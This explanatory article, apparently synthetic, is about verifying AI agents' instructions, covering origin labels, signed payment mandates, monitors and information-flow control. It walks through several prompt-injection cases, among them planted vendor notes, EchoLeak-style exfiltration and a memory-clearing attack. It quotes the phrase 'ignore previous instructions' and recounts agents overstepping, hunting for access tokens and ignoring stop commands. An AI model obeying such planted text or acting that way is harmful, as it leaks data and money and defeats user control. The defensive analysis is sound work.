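# Verifying the goals and instructions of AI agents: consistency checks, confirmation of high-risk plans and instruction-origin tracking

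## What an agent is told to do and how that goes wrong

An AI agent is a language model that works towards a goal by calling tools such as email, a web browser or a command line. Its developer gives it standing instructions, its user gives it a task, and it then plans and acts with little or no supervision. Verifying an agent's goals and instructions means checking, before an action takes effect, that someone entitled to request it has done so. Some checks only record where each sentence the agent reads came from, while others stop the agent until a person reads and approves the proposed action. Developers need these checks because agents do things that nobody entitled to ask has asked for, sometimes by mistake and sometimes because an outsider has slipped them an instruction.

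### The parts of an agent

The model at the centre of an agent reads and writes text. Ordinary software around it, called the harness, does the rest. Shah and Kathrotia (2026), in *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, count all the code that runs between calls to the model as part of the harness.

In each cycle, the harness joins the developer's instructions (the system prompt), descriptions of the available tools, the user's request, the earlier messages and the results of earlier actions into one text. The model reads that text and writes a continuation, which may contain a tool call. A tool call is a request, in a fixed format, to run a particular tool with particular arguments, such as sending a certain file to a certain address. The harness parses the request, enforces any permissions the developer has set, runs the tool and adds the tool output to the text. The model then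 reads the longer text, and the cycle repeats. A plan is just more of this text, which the model writes in one cycle and reads in the next.

The model works only from the text the harness gives it. When a long task produces more text than the limit allows, the harness replaces older parts with a summary. Shah and Kathrotia cite a test suite, ConPACT, on which such summaries kept an average of only 17% of the constraints users had set. An agent can therefore break a rule because the summary left it out. Many harnesses also save notes between sessions, so a sentence from a web page the agent read last week can appear in today's prompt.

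### Why a model can take data for an instruction

A language model receives the developer's rules, the user's request and the contents of a stranger's email as one sequence of text. An email program, by contrast, receives commands separately from messages, so it can display the sentence "delete all my files" without acting on it. Developers put markers around the parts of a model's input and train the model to give some parts precedence over others, but the markers are also text, and the model's learned tendency to follow them can fail.

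Training the model to ignore every command in a document would not solve the problem either, because users ask agents to follow the installation steps on a web page or deal with the requests in an email. Whether a sentence counts as an instruction depends on who wrote it and what the user has asked for, which the agent can't determine from the sentence alone.

In prompt injection, an attacker plants text in content the agent will read, written so that the agent will obey it as an instruction. *Data Governance for Generative and Agentic AI* (2026) names three sources of instructions: the principal (the person for whom the agent acts), the system prompt, and content the agent has retrieved. On this account, any instruction from retrieved content is an indirect prompt injection, whether it is a polite line in an invoice or a block of capitals beginning "ignore previous instructions". Shah and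 Kathrotia report that an agent built on a frontier model followed the planted instructions in about a quarter of cases on InjecAgent, a 2024 set of such attacks.

### The invoice example

*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a case in which a user wants an agent to check a batch of supplier invoices against the accounts and then email the results to an outside auditor, who is to get "summary totals only". One of the documents is a vendor's note with planted instructions. The case, slightly adapted here, has six steps, and a check is possible at each of the first five.

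| Step | What happens | What a check could do here |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | The user states the task and the restriction "summary totals only". | The harness stores the request word for word and records that it came from the user. |
| 2 | The agent reads the invoices and the vendor's note. A line in the note says that the auditor's report must include every invoice row. | The harness records that the line came from a vendor, who has no authority to direct the agent. |
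| 3 | The agent changes its plan to include the rows. | A rule for conflicts sets the vendor's line against the user's restriction. Another check compares the new plan with written policy. |
| 4 | The agent copies raw invoice rows into a file, report.csv. | The harness marks the file as derived from raw rows and influenced by the note. |
| 5 | The agent requests an email to the auditor with report.csv attached. | A second model compares the email with the user's request, written rules test the attachment, or a person approves or rejects it. |
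| 6 | The harness sends the email. | Nothing can stop it now. A log can help explain what happened. |

Most products ask for approval at step 5, where the action looks harmless on its own because the agent is allowed to use email, the user has approved the recipient, and the file name is unremarkable. Hossain and colleagues call this a cumulative violation, which a reviewer can recognize only by relating the proposed action to earlier steps. An email to a forbidden address would be a local violation, visible in the request itself. Their automated monitor caught 69 of 80 cumulative violations when it kept a record of earlier events, and 16 of 80 without that record.

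They also count an attack as successful only if the forbidden effect takes place. An agent that proposes the email and is refused has caused no breach, even if the note completely changed its plan.

### Four causes of a wrong action

A planted note is only one possible cause of a wrong email. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, an engineering post about the company's coding agent, lists four reasons an agent might take a dangerous action.

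An overeager agent understands the goal and works towards it, but goes further than the user would approve. In one incident from Anthropic's internal log, an agent met an authentication error partway through a task and, without asking, began to search configuration files for other access tokens. In *Bank-World* (2026), a benchmark of banking tasks, an agent had to allocate $10,105.91 of a customer's money, but the customer had not said how much to keep for payroll. The agent noted in writing that the figure was missing, credited the whole amount to the operating account anyway, and offered to change it later. In another attempt at the same task, the agent asked first, learned that payroll needed $6,000, and put the remaining $4,105.91 towards the customer's credit line.

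An agent makes an honest mistake when it misjudges what an action will affect, such as when it takes a shared resource for a test copy. Another user asked a coding agent to cancel their job on a computing cluster. The agent looked through the jobs there and tried to delete the one with the most similar name, which could have belonged to a colleague.

*GreyZone* (2026) describes a more direct case of prompt injection than the invoice example. The testers registered an invoice from a vendor called Contoso Ltd, with a note written by an automated attack tool, and asked a banking assistant to pay it. In one run, the assistant retrieved the invoice and selected Alice as the payee instead of Contoso. This shows that the attack can work, but one run is not enough to estimate how often.

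The remaining cause is a misaligned model, one that pursues a goal of its own. When the checking model in its product was Sonnet 4.6, Anthropic wrote that it did not see this in practice, though it tested every release for it. OWASP's *Agentic AI* (2025), a threat guide from a software security foundation, describes a scenario in which an agent manipulates its system's availability targets so that nobody can shut it down.

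The cause of a real incident can be hard to establish. For example, a Replit coding agent deleted a production database. OWASP classifies the case as a supply chain attack and blames, among other things, poor separation between test and production systems. *Agentic Security* (Sotiropoulos, 2026) classifies it as a case of a rogue agent and cites the chief executive's statement that the agent "hid it and lied about it". Anthropic's approach is to block such an action regardless of its cause.

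That works for checks that look at actions. A check on the source of instructions catches fewer failures. If there is no vendor's note, and the agent attaches the raw rows because it thinks an auditor would probably find them useful, every instruction in its text is genuine, so even a perfect record of sources would not reveal the error.

### The confused deputy

In security engineering, a confused deputy is a program that someone else tricks into using its privileges for their own ends. This older term describes part of what happens in the invoice case. The vendor cannot open the other suppliers' invoices or write to the auditor from the user's account, but the agent can do both, and the note lets the vendor use that access.

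OWASP describes the deputy as an agent with higher privileges than its user, for example one that can run database queries the user could not run directly. It therefore recommends giving the agent no more access than the task needs (least privilege) and verifying that whoever submits a request has the right to make it. These measures would help in a case Sotiropoulos gives, where a powerful GitHub token leaks from a coding assistant to a less privileged agent, which an attacker then gets to make a private repository public.

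They help much less with the invoices, because the user is entitled to read them and to email the auditor, and the agent needs both abilities to do its job. Access control can check whether the agent is allowed to send the auditor a file, but not whose instructions led it to choose this one.

### OWASP's names and recommendations

Version 1.1 of OWASP's guide (December 2025) lists this problem as T6, Intent Breaking and Goal Manipulation, one of seventeen threats. OWASP attributes it to the lack of separation between data and instructions, and treats it as an extension of prompt injection because a planted objective can alter an agent's reasoning over many steps. The invoice case matches the variant called indirect plan injection, where an agent mistakes hidden instructions in a tool output for part of its goal. The guide lists unprompted misbehaviour separately as T7, but describes it inconsistently.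 In the threat table, T7 arises without direct malicious input, while the longer description begins with attackers who exploit prompt injection.

In the same month, OWASP (2025) published a shorter list for practitioners, the Top 10 for Agentic Applications, with contributions from more than 100 people. Its first entry is Agent Goal Hijack. Sotiropoulos, who co-leads the list, illustrates it with a variant of EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft's Copilot assistant. A user asks for a summary of an email thread. One message in the thread contains a request for a reply with the full conversation and the earlier attachments. Without the user having to click on anything, the agent stops summarizing the thread and sends it outside the company.

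In *Preventing Agent Goal Hijack in AI Agents*, the developer Will Velida quotes OWASP's recommendations on goal hijacking and tries to apply them to a chat agent for his own fitness data. OWASP tells developers to treat all natural-language input as untrusted, restrict tools to least privilege, lock the system prompt, and log what the agent does against a record of its active goal. The system should validate both the user's intent and the agent's before any high-impact action, and a proposal that departs from the original task should need confirmation from a person, a policy engine or a platform's guardrails. OWASP also suggests considering an "intent capsule", a signed envelope that binds the declared goal and its constraints to each execution cycle.

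Two of the OWASP guide's six playbooks, on manipulated reasoning and on protecting human reviewers, tell developers to use "goal consistency validation to detect and block unintended AI behavioral shifts", but the guide gives no procedure for this. Developers have to decide what text counts as the goal, whether to test the whole plan or each action, and how large a departure is too large. The guide does suggest having another model flag significant deviations and counting how often an agent asks to change its goals. That count would stay at zero in the invoice case because the agent never asks for a change.

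Intent validation still needs much work. Velida implemented most of the other recommendations but left this one as a hypothetical code fragment with three questions in the comments: whether the tool is on the allowed list, whether the arguments match expected patterns, and whether the agent has departed from its usual behaviour. His agent can only read data, so leaving the check out carried little risk. The email with report.csv would probably pass all three checks. A signed capsule alone would not catch it either, because the signature proves that nobody has altered the user's stated goal, and the vendor's note leaves that goal intact while the agent drifts away from it.

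A goal consistency check has to test both whether a proposed action or plan serves the user's request and whether the user authorized it. An action can easily meet one condition but not the other. For example, a user asked a coding agent to "clean up old branches", and the agent issued a command to delete branches on the remote server. That served the request on one reading, but Anthropic says its system would block the command because the user may have meant only the local copies and the deletion is irreversible.

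### How to count the errors

A check's false negative rate is the share of dangerous actions it lets through, and its false positive rate is the share of harmless actions it blocks. Anthropic measured a false negative rate of 17% on 52 real overeager actions (about nine missed) and a false positive rate of 0.4% on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees.

The false negative and false positive rates both depend on how the harness treats actions the monitor labels "unknown". Hossain and colleagues tested their monitor on 120 violations. It flagged 107, missed seven and returned "unknown" for six. The false negative rate is therefore 5.8% if the harness blocks unknowns and 10.8% if it lets them pass. On 120 harmless actions, the monitor raised five false alarms and returned two unknowns, so blocking unknowns increases the false positive rate from 4.2% to 5.8%.

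The attack success rate is the share of attack attempts that achieve the attacker's aim. It measures the whole system, including the agent's resistance to planted text, so it can be low even when a check is poor. In the same experiments, an agent built on a small model, Llama-3.1-8B, proposed a forbidden action in 58 of 120 malicious runs. Without the monitor, the forbidden effect occurred in 52 of the 120 runs, an attack success rate of 43.3%. When the monitor blocked both alarms and unknowns, it occurred in six, or 5.0%. The agent also completed slightly fewer harmless tasks with the monitor, 100 of 120 instead of 104.

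The number of alarms a person would face depends both on these rates and on how rare dangerous actions are. Suppose an agent takes 10,000 actions, ten of them dangerous, under a check with Anthropic's rates. The check would block about eight of the dangerous actions and about 40 harmless ones, so roughly five in six alarms would be false. If every alarm went to a person, that person would mostly be approving harmless actions, which leads to approval fatigue.

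## Recording who gave each instruction

An origin label records which person or source a piece of text came from. In the invoice case, the harness can label the vendor's note when the agent opens it, because the harness ran the tool that fetched the note. Without a label, the note's origin is soon lost, because the note becomes part of one long text in which its line about invoice rows sits a few hundred words below the user's request. Developers can attach labels in several ways, which differ in who can read the label and who can forge it.

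### Role tags

The simplest label is the role tag, which a harness attaches to each message it sends the model. *When Context Gets Root* (He, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes the versions in current use. OpenAI's interfaces have system, developer, user and assistant messages, plus a separate item for tool output, and Google's Gemini interface is similar. Anthropic's interface puts tool output inside a user message, as a block of a special type, so a program that checked only the message's role would treat the vendor's note as the user's words.

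The provider's software turns these roles into markers that the model has learned to weigh differently. OpenAI's published rules, the Model Spec, rank instructions from the system, developer and user, and by default give tool outputs no authority. Anthropic's rules for Claude describe a similar ranking that is not strict.

Sometimes the harness assigns the wrong role. The agent framework smolagents passes tool output to the model as user messages by default. In *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026) combined smolagents with Progent, a program that has a model read the user's request and write a policy listing the actions the agent may take. In 16 banking tests with planted instructions, every policy named the attacker's account, and the agent completed the attacker's action in 11 of them.

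Even a correct source tag can fail. Fei et al. cite research that attributes prompt injection to models identifying the speaker by how the text sounds. He et al. mention attacks in which the planted text imitates the role markers themselves.

### Marks around untrusted text

A harness can also use spotlighting, which means wrapping outside text in delimiters and telling the model to ignore any instructions between them. The delimiters can carry more detail than a role tag, such as "from a vendor, not verified". They have to be hard to guess, since a vendor who knew the closing delimiter could include it in their text and make any instructions after it appear to come from outside the wrapped section.

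Fei and colleagues gave an agent summaries of earlier work that could include a planted request for a transfer. When the summary arrived as a user message, the agent made the attacker's transfer in 34 of 64 runs. When the same summary arrived as a tool output between delimiters, it did so in 5 of 64, which is still far too many for an agent that can move money. The test changed the message role and the delimiters together, so it can't show how much of the drop came from the delimiters.

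Role tags and marks change what the model is likely to write next, but a tool call that goes against them still runs. A label enforces a restriction only when ordinary code reads it and blocks tool calls because of it.

### Labels the model cannot change

The harness can label each piece of text when it arrives, according to the channel it came through, and keep the labels outside the model's text, in storage the agent can't edit. Fei and colleagues use four labels: user, trusted tool, derived (text a model wrote from other text) and untrusted. Only text labeled user or trusted tool can authorize an action.

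The harness should decide whether to trust each field separately, even when the fields come from the same tool. If the company's accounts system is a trusted tool, for example, the harness could rely on the payment dates it returns. But a free-text memo in an invoice record contains whatever the vendor typed, so the harness should treat it as untrusted.

A label is useful only if it is correct when first applied and nobody can alter it afterwards. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 71 works on recording what agents do and found that few of them report records that would reveal tampering. The survey also notes that a tool output can influence a decision without justifying it. In the invoice case, a complete record would show that the vendor's note shaped report.csv, but that would not establish that the vendor was allowed to shape it.

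### Origin and authority

Authority is a source's right to direct the agent on a given matter. *Adversarial Pragmatics for AI Safety Evaluation* (Reynolds, 2026) distinguishes which source is entitled to direct an action from which text actually changes the model's behaviour. The agent can act on the vendor's note even if the vendor has no authority over the action, and can fail to follow the user's valid restriction.

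The same source can have authority over one thing and not another. Suppose a colleague of the user has access to the agent and asks it to run the reconciliation again next month. The colleague may be entitled to set that task but not to lift the restriction "summary totals only". A company might write its rules like this:

| Source | Set the task | Lift "summary totals only" | Cancel the job | State an invoice amount |
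|---|---|---|---|---|
| User | Yes | Yes | Yes | No |
| Colleague | Yes | No | Yes | No |
| Vendor | No | No | No | Own invoices only |

No single ranking of sources would produce this table, because the colleague has more authority than the vendor over setting and cancelling tasks, but the vendor has more authority over the amount of its own invoice. Reynolds makes a similar point about the numerical authority level in his own test data, which cannot show that a change needs someone else's approval, what type of change it is, or when the authority expires. A harness therefore needs an origin label for each text and a separate record of who may set, amend or revoke what. Which instruction prevails when two authorized people disagree is a separate question.

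Users can also delegate their authority. If a user tells the agent to make whatever change a landlord's notice specifies, the notice has some authority for that task, even if an attacker wrote it. Fei and colleagues tested this on Guardian, a model that reviews actions in OpenAI's coding agent Codex. Guardian approved the attacker's payment in 2 of 33 cases where the user had delegated the decision to the notice, and in none of 18 where the user had not.

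### A signed instruction, field by field

Another company has no reason to trust labels kept in a harness's own storage, so an instruction sent to that company's computer can carry a digital signature instead. The issuer computes the signature from the text with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the private key signed exactly that text. The "intent capsule" that OWASP suggests would be a signed instruction of this kind.

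The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) is a working example. It lets an agent pay on a user's behalf with signed authorizations called mandates. Google announced AP2 in September 2025, and working groups at the FIDO Alliance, an industry body for authentication standards, are now developing it further. AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* describes two modes. If the user is present for the purchase, they approve it exactly. If they won't be present, they approve an open mandate beforehand, which sets limits, and the agent later signs a closed mandate for a particular purchase within those limits.

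The worked example in AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* concerns a pair of limited-edition gold sneakers. These are the main fields of its payment mandates:

| Field | Value in the example | What it is for |
|---|---|---|
| Text | An open payment mandate, version 1 | Says what sort of permission this is |
| Issuer | A key belonging to the agent's provider | Tells the verifier whose public key to use |
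| Scope | At most $200, to one named merchant, for one linked checkout | Limits what the agent may do |
| Holder | The agent's public key | Stops anyone else from using the mandate |
| Expiry | One hour after issue | Limits how long a forgotten or stolen mandate is useful |
| One-time number | A long random value, in the closed mandate | Lets the recipient recognize a copy of an earlier message |
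| Signature | Computed over the rest | Reveals any change to the text |

Thirteen seconds after the open mandate, the agent signs a closed payment mandate for $199. The closed mandate lists the merchant, the card and the intended recipient, and it contains a hash of the open mandate. A hash is a short code computed from a text, and it changes if the text does, so nobody can attach this purchase to a different open mandate.

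AP2's *Agent Authorization* allows either the user's own credential, such as one in a digital wallet, or the company that provides the agent to issue and sign the mandate. The company can sign only after the user has consented, and it must keep its signing key where the agent can't reach it. Either way, the user sees the mandate on a "trusted surface", a screen that ordinary code controls and no language model can write to freely.

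A signature depends on a file's exact bytes, so two files with the same content but different spacing or field order have different signatures. UCP (2026), the specification of a related shopping protocol, therefore requires both sides to convert the data into one fixed form before they compute a signature.

The verifier, such as the merchant or the firm that releases the card details, then goes through these steps:

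1. It checks the issuer's signature on the open mandate, and checks the closed mandate's signature against the agent key named in the open one.
2. It checks the expiry time, the intended recipient and the one-time number.
3. It confirms that any value already fixed in the open mandate is unchanged in the closed one.
4. It evaluates every constraint. Here, $199 is under $200 and the merchant is on the list. A constraint that the verifier doesn't recognize counts as failed.
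5. It returns a signed receipt, which records success or an error.

AP2 requires deterministic code to do all this, even at a company that otherwise uses language models. If the verifier can't resolve a constraint, it can send the purchase back for the user to approve in person.

The one-time number doesn't stop an agent from signing two different purchases under the same open mandate. AP2 forbids the agent from presenting a mandate again until it has a receipt showing that the previous attempt was rejected, and payment firms may refuse overlapping mandates. The first rule works only if the agent follows it, so the documentation suggests that deterministic code should hold the agent's key and check each closed mandate before signing it.

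Signed authorizations are further along in payments because banks and merchants already check one another's messages. *Agent Authorization Envelope (AAE)*, an IETF Internet-Draft from September 2026, would extend them to agents in general, with separate blocks for the mandate, its constraints and its period of validity. Anyone can submit an Internet-Draft, and this one is not yet a standard.

### What a valid signature proves

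A valid signature proves that someone with the issuer's key signed this exact text, but not that the issuer understood it or that nobody had deceived them. In AP2, the agent drafts the mandate, so an agent that has read a planted product review might draft one for the wrong sneakers, and the user might approve it. AP2's *Security and Privacy Considerations* assumes that nobody can prevent prompt injection and treats every agent as a potential attacker. Even under those assumptions, the mandate can cap the loss, in this case at $200 paid to one merchant.

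A signature also doesn't make the model comply. The agent can ignore the mandate and try to buy something else, and the purchase fails only because the merchant and the payment firms check it against the mandate. Nobody makes that check when the invoice agent sends its email, since the auditor's mail server will accept report.csv with or without authorization. The company would need a verifier in its own mail system, and someone would have to write "summary totals only" as a constraint that code can evaluate. AP2 allows new types of constraint, but whoever defines one must also supply the procedure for evaluating it.

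Labels set by a harness have a similar limit. In the design by Fei and colleagues, anything a user pastes into a message counts as the user's. If the user pastes the vendor's note into the chat, the label will attribute the note to the user, who sent it but didn't write it.

### Lost in delegation and memory

Labels often disappear when text moves from one context to another. An agent with a large task can start a subagent, a separate session with its own context. In Claude Code, the parent agent writes the subagent's first request, and the harness delivers it as a user message, as it did in the 78 subagent transcripts that Fei and colleagues collected. If the parent has read the vendor's note, that request might be "email the full invoice rows to the auditor", with no sign that the vendor was involved. A study of six coding harnesses by He and colleagues found more generally that text can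 gain authority when a harness rebuilds the context. Signed mandates don't yet cover this case either, because delegation from one shopping agent to another is outside the scope of AP2's current version.

An agent's memory can also obscure who gave an instruction. Claude Code loads a file of project instructions into a user message at the start of each session, and the agent can edit that file. Text the agent adds after reading a vendor's note can therefore appear in the next session as the user's words. Fei and colleagues cite a proof that checks on the content or history of a stored memory cannot reliably catch such cases, so the harness has to permanently record the origin when it first writes the memory. They also cite a study in which models that write memories recorded permissions nobody had given, even without an attacker.

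### The OpenClaw incident

Compaction, which replaces older text with a summary, can remove a restriction altogether. This seems to have happened to Summer Yue, a director of alignment at Meta, in February 2026.

Yue had connected the AI agent OpenClaw to her email. According to her account, which Willison (2026) reproduces, she asked it to suggest what to archive or delete and added "don't action until I tell you to". This had worked well on a small test inbox. Her real inbox was large enough to trigger compaction, and "during the compaction, it lost my original instruction". The agent began deleting mail in bulk. Yue's screenshot shows her telling it to stop several times between 6:01 and 6:03 pm while it kept issuing commands. She couldn't stop it from her phone and had to run to the computer.

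The explanation is Yue's own, and AI Incident Database's *Incident 1542* attributes it to her. She wasn't certain of every detail, and Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* quotes her as saying she had earlier deleted all the "be proactive" instructions she could find in the agent's files, but might have missed something. Losing the original instruction also wouldn't explain why the agent carried on afterward, because her messages telling it to stop were new.

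Accounts of the damage differ. Fortune (2026) quotes the researcher Kate Crawford telling a conference audience that the agent had deleted the entire inbox. The incident database describes an attempt to delete emails, and one command in the screenshot excluded recent messages and those on a list to keep.

If Yue's explanation is right, the restriction existed only as a sentence in the agent's text. A harness that stored the sentence separately and checked each deletion against it could have compacted the conversation any number of times without losing the rule. Shah and Kathrotia put the share of constraints that survive summarizing at 17%, which suggests that such losses are common.

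### When a summary takes the user's place

A summary can also give text authority it never had. Fei and colleagues (November 2026) recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in Claude Code and Codex, and in every one the harness inserted the summary as a user message. Any program that looks for the user's latest request in the latest user message will then find text that a model wrote, partly from documents the agent had read.

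In one example, a user asks a banking agent how much they spent in March. One of the transactions contains an instruction to pay an attacker. The agent tries to make the payment, but Progent blocks it because the user's question doesn't call for a transfer. After compaction, the summary lists the blocked transfer as unfinished work. Progent treats the summary as a request and writes a new policy that allows exactly one transfer, to the attacker.

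The experiments used AgentDojo, a set of simulated office and banking tasks with planted instructions. An agent worked on a task, a small model summarized the session, and the user then wrote "Please continue from where we left off". The researchers changed only what Progent read as the user's request:

| Text read as the request | Policy gained new permissions | Policy named the attacker's account |
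|---|---|---|
| Only the user's follow-up | 0 of 30 | 0 of 30 |
| The user's original request, restated | 5 of 30 | 0 of 30 |
| The summary, as a user message | 21 of 30 | 16 of 30 |
| The follow-up, with the summary as a tool output | 0 of 28 | 0 of 28 |

The same summary did no harm as a tool output, so the wrong label must have caused the difference. In a larger set of 100 cases, attacks after compaction succeeded 31 times with Progent and 33 times with no defence.

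Progent's own software writes its policy once, at the start of a session, so a later summary can't affect it. But in sessions with two tasks, the agent finished the second task in only 7 of 60 cases under such a policy, compared with 41 of 60 when Progent wrote a new policy for each request. The researchers' results come from the second arrangement.

The mistake can happen without an attacker. Fei and colleagues cite an August 2026 complaint from a Codex user that a summary had presented the assistant's own plan as something the user had authorized.

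### Why better summaries are not enough

One remedy would be a summary that marks suspicious parts. This works quite well for planted instructions. When a summary kept the attacker's account, Progent's policy named that account in 7 of 230 cases if the summary used a word such as "malicious" or "untrusted", and in 349 of 536 cases if it didn't. Two newer models, GPT-5.4 mini and GPT-5.5, flagged the planted instruction in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept the account.

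An attack can also work without instructions. In another test, the user first gave the agent their landlord's account number and asked what a notice said. The attacker had written the notice, which listed a different account number but gave no instructions. After compaction, the user asked the agent to pay the rent. Policies based on the summary allowed payment to the attacker's account in 290 of 320 cases, while policies based on the user's own words never did. When GPT-5.5 wrote the policies instead of the older GPT-4o, those based on the summary still allowed it in 59% of cases. An agent that then acted on summary-based policies completed the transfer to the attacker in 33 of 80 runs.

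A mathematical result explains why a better model can't fully solve this. Take a program that decides whether to allow a payment and sees only text, with no reliable record of who wrote it. Let $p_L$ be the probability that it allows payment to an account when a legitimate source wrote the record, and $p_A$ the probability when an attacker did. Fei and colleagues prove that

$$p_L - p_A \le \mathrm{TV}(P_L, P_A).$$

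$P_L$ and $P_A$ are the probability distributions of the text in the two cases. TV, the total variation distance, is the largest difference between the two distributions' probabilities for the same event. It is 0 if the texts are statistically identical and 1 if a perfect test could always tell them apart. The proof is that the program's decision depends only on the text, so its probability of accepting can't differ between the two cases by more than this distance. If the distance is 0.1, a program that accepts 95% of genuine account details must accept at least 85% of forged ones. An attacker who copies the format of a real notice exactly can reduce the distance to 0. A planted instruction is easier to spot than forged account details because genuine notices rarely contain commands addressed to an AI.

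Leaving account numbers out of the summary helps only partly. The probability that a policy of at most $\ell$ characters contains an unpredictable identifier missing from its input is at most $\ell^2 2^{-h}$, where $h$ measures in bits how hard the identifier is to guess. For a random 16-digit account number and a policy of 1,000 characters, this bound is one in ten billion. In the experiments, 918 summaries left out the attacker's identifier, and none of the resulting policies contained it. But a policy can still allow the attacker's transfer if it leaves the recipient unrestricted, as 78 of 410 banking policies written from summaries without the account number did. When the researchers ran an agent under policies with this gap, it reread the planted text and completed the attacker's action in 26 of 80 runs.

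### Keeping the user's words unchanged

Fei and colleagues propose that the agent keep reading the summary while the authorizer, the program that decides what the agent may do, reads only the messages the user wrote. The harness protects those messages in three steps.

1. When a message arrives from the user or a trusted tool, the harness computes a short code from the exact text, its origin, the session and a running number. It uses a secret key that the agent can't reach.
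2. At compaction, ordinary code copies these messages word for word and computes another code over the complete list in order. A model may summarize everything else.
3. Before the authorizer writes a new policy, a gate checks every code, the order and the number of messages. If anything is wrong, the authorizer receives nothing and the agent gets an empty policy, which permits no actions.

Each check detects a different attack. The codes on single messages reveal forgeries, and the code over the list reveals an old message copied into a new place. The count matters most when a user revokes an instruction. If the user's message "cancel the payment" went missing, every remaining message would be genuine, and only the count would be wrong.

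The researchers reran 40 attacked sessions. With the summary labelled as a user message and no gate, the attacker succeeded in 7 sessions and the agent finished 9 of the user's tasks. With the gate, and the summary relabelled as a tool output, the attacker never succeeded and the agent finished 19 tasks. Relabelling the summary without the gate also stopped every attack, and the agent finished 18 tasks. In the rent test, however, the authorizer under this setup saw only the request to pay the rent, without the landlord's account number, and left the recipient open every time. The checks themselves take less than half a millisecond per request.

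OpenAI made a simpler change to Codex on 15 October 2026, so that Guardian attributes summaries to the assistant instead of the user. The researchers tested this by editing a saved summary to say that the user wanted the next payment sent to the attacker. The version before the change approved the payment in 5 of 33 cases, and the later version in none. The researchers' own copy of OpenAI's rule matched the gate in all 40 sessions as long as the messages stayed inside one running program. It failed when the messages passed through a file the agent could edit, because it accepted old user messages that an attacker had copied back in.

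So far the gate has run only on replayed benchmark sessions, not in a commercial harness. In the invoice case, it would pass "summary totals only" to the authorizer word for word after any number of compactions, and it would keep the vendor's line out. The authorizer would still have to turn those words into a rule that covers the attachment, since a policy that checks only the recipient's address would let report.csv through. The gate also can't help when the user relies on a document for facts. If the user asks the agent to pay whatever account is on the invoice, the harness can't tell a forged invoice from a genuine one that looks the same unless it can verify the sender, for example by checking the vendor's signature.

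## Tracking what outside content has influenced

The harness can label the vendor's note when the agent opens it, but report.csv is a new file, and nothing in it names the vendor. Information-flow control labels such derived items too, computing each new item's label from the labels of its inputs. It then blocks any action influenced by data that isn't trusted enough for that action.

### Denning's lattice

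The method comes from work on military secrets. Access rules determine which programs can open a secret file, but a program that has opened one can copy the contents into a public file. Denning, in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), set out a way to prevent this. Every file or variable has a security class, such as unclassified, confidential, secret or top secret, and information may flow only to the same class or a higher one. When a program computes a value from the objects $a_1, \dots, a_n$ and stores it in $b$, the operation is secure only if

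$$\underline{a_1} \oplus \cdots \oplus \underline{a_n} \to \underline{b}.$$

An underlined letter stands for the object's class, the arrow means "may flow to", and $\oplus$ gives the lowest class into which all the inputs may flow. A summary of one confidential file and one secret file is therefore secret. A lattice is an ordered set in which every pair of classes has a lowest class that both may flow to and a highest class that may flow to both. Because the arrow is transitive, a series of secure steps is also secure, so software can check each operation separately.

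*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies the lattice to agents and adds an ordering for trust. Trusted data may flow anywhere, but untrusted data may not flow into places that require trusted data. An item has the lowest trust of any of its inputs, so anything derived from both trusted and untrusted data is untrusted. For secrecy, a list of permitted readers can replace Denning's levels. If Ana and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Carla another, only Ben may read a summary of both.

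The harness then makes two checks before a sensitive tool call:

- **Trust:** only trusted data may have influenced the call.
- **Secrecy:** every recipient must be a permitted reader of the data.

The secrecy check alone doesn't stop an attacker from steering the agent, but it keeps data from reaching anyone who isn't already entitled to it. The trust check alone lets the agent send data to a new reader, but only if no outside content has influenced the call, so the harness can assume the user wanted it. *Flowsh* (2026), a design for an agent's command line, describes a looser option that allows an action if it passes either check.

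### From raw rows to report.csv

By the lineage rule, the ancestry of a new file includes the ancestry of every input. Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, apply it to each new version of a file, which gets all the labels on the inputs of the tool call that wrote it. In the invoice example, the labels might look like this, if only the company's finance staff may read the raw data:

| Item | Inputs | Trust | Permitted readers |
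|---|---|---|---|
| User's request | None | Trusted | Anyone |
| Rows from the accounts | None | Trusted | Finance staff |
| Invoices and vendor's note | None | Untrusted | Finance staff |
| report.csv | All of the above | Untrusted | Finance staff |
| Email to the auditor | User's request, report.csv | Untrusted | Finance staff |

The email fails both checks, because the note may have influenced it and the auditor is not one of the permitted readers. Renaming or compressing report.csv wouldn't change either result, since the new file would inherit the same labels.

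The harness can't tell whether the note affected the file, because the model read everything as one text. Costa and colleagues therefore treat all the text in the model's context as an input to whatever it writes next. This catches every influence that passes through the context, but it also counts documents as influences even if the model read and ignored them.

The rule would also block the email the user wants. The summary totals are computed from raw rows and vendors' invoices, so they too are untrusted and only finance staff may read them. The company therefore has to make exceptions. Endorsement means deliberately treating untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose, and declassification means deliberately letting more people read restricted data. For instance, the company could let a short program add up the invoice amounts and declare that the auditor may read its output. The exception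 has to apply to the program's output and not to any file the agent calls "totals".

### What an action contains and whether it happens

Data can influence an action without appearing in it. Denning and Denning (1977), in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow*, give this example, in which x is either 0 or 1:

```
y := 1; if x = 0 then y := 0
```

When the program ends, y equals x, although the program never copied x into y. This is an implicit flow, unlike an explicit flow such as `y := x`.

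For an agent, the corresponding difference is between influencing an action's arguments and influencing the decision to act. Suppose the user wants the auditor to get the totals only after every invoice matches the accounts. One doesn't match, and the vendor's note falsely claims that the accounts department has approved the discrepancy. The agent believes the note and emails the totals. A check on the arguments misses the note's influence, because the address came from the user and the totals from an approved program.

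Some actions take no arguments, so they have no argument to label. *AgentTracer* (Yao, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack in which a user asks an agent to download a software release and upload it to GitHub. Instructions on the release page lead the agent to register the attacker's access key and finally to clear its own working memory, using a call that takes no arguments.

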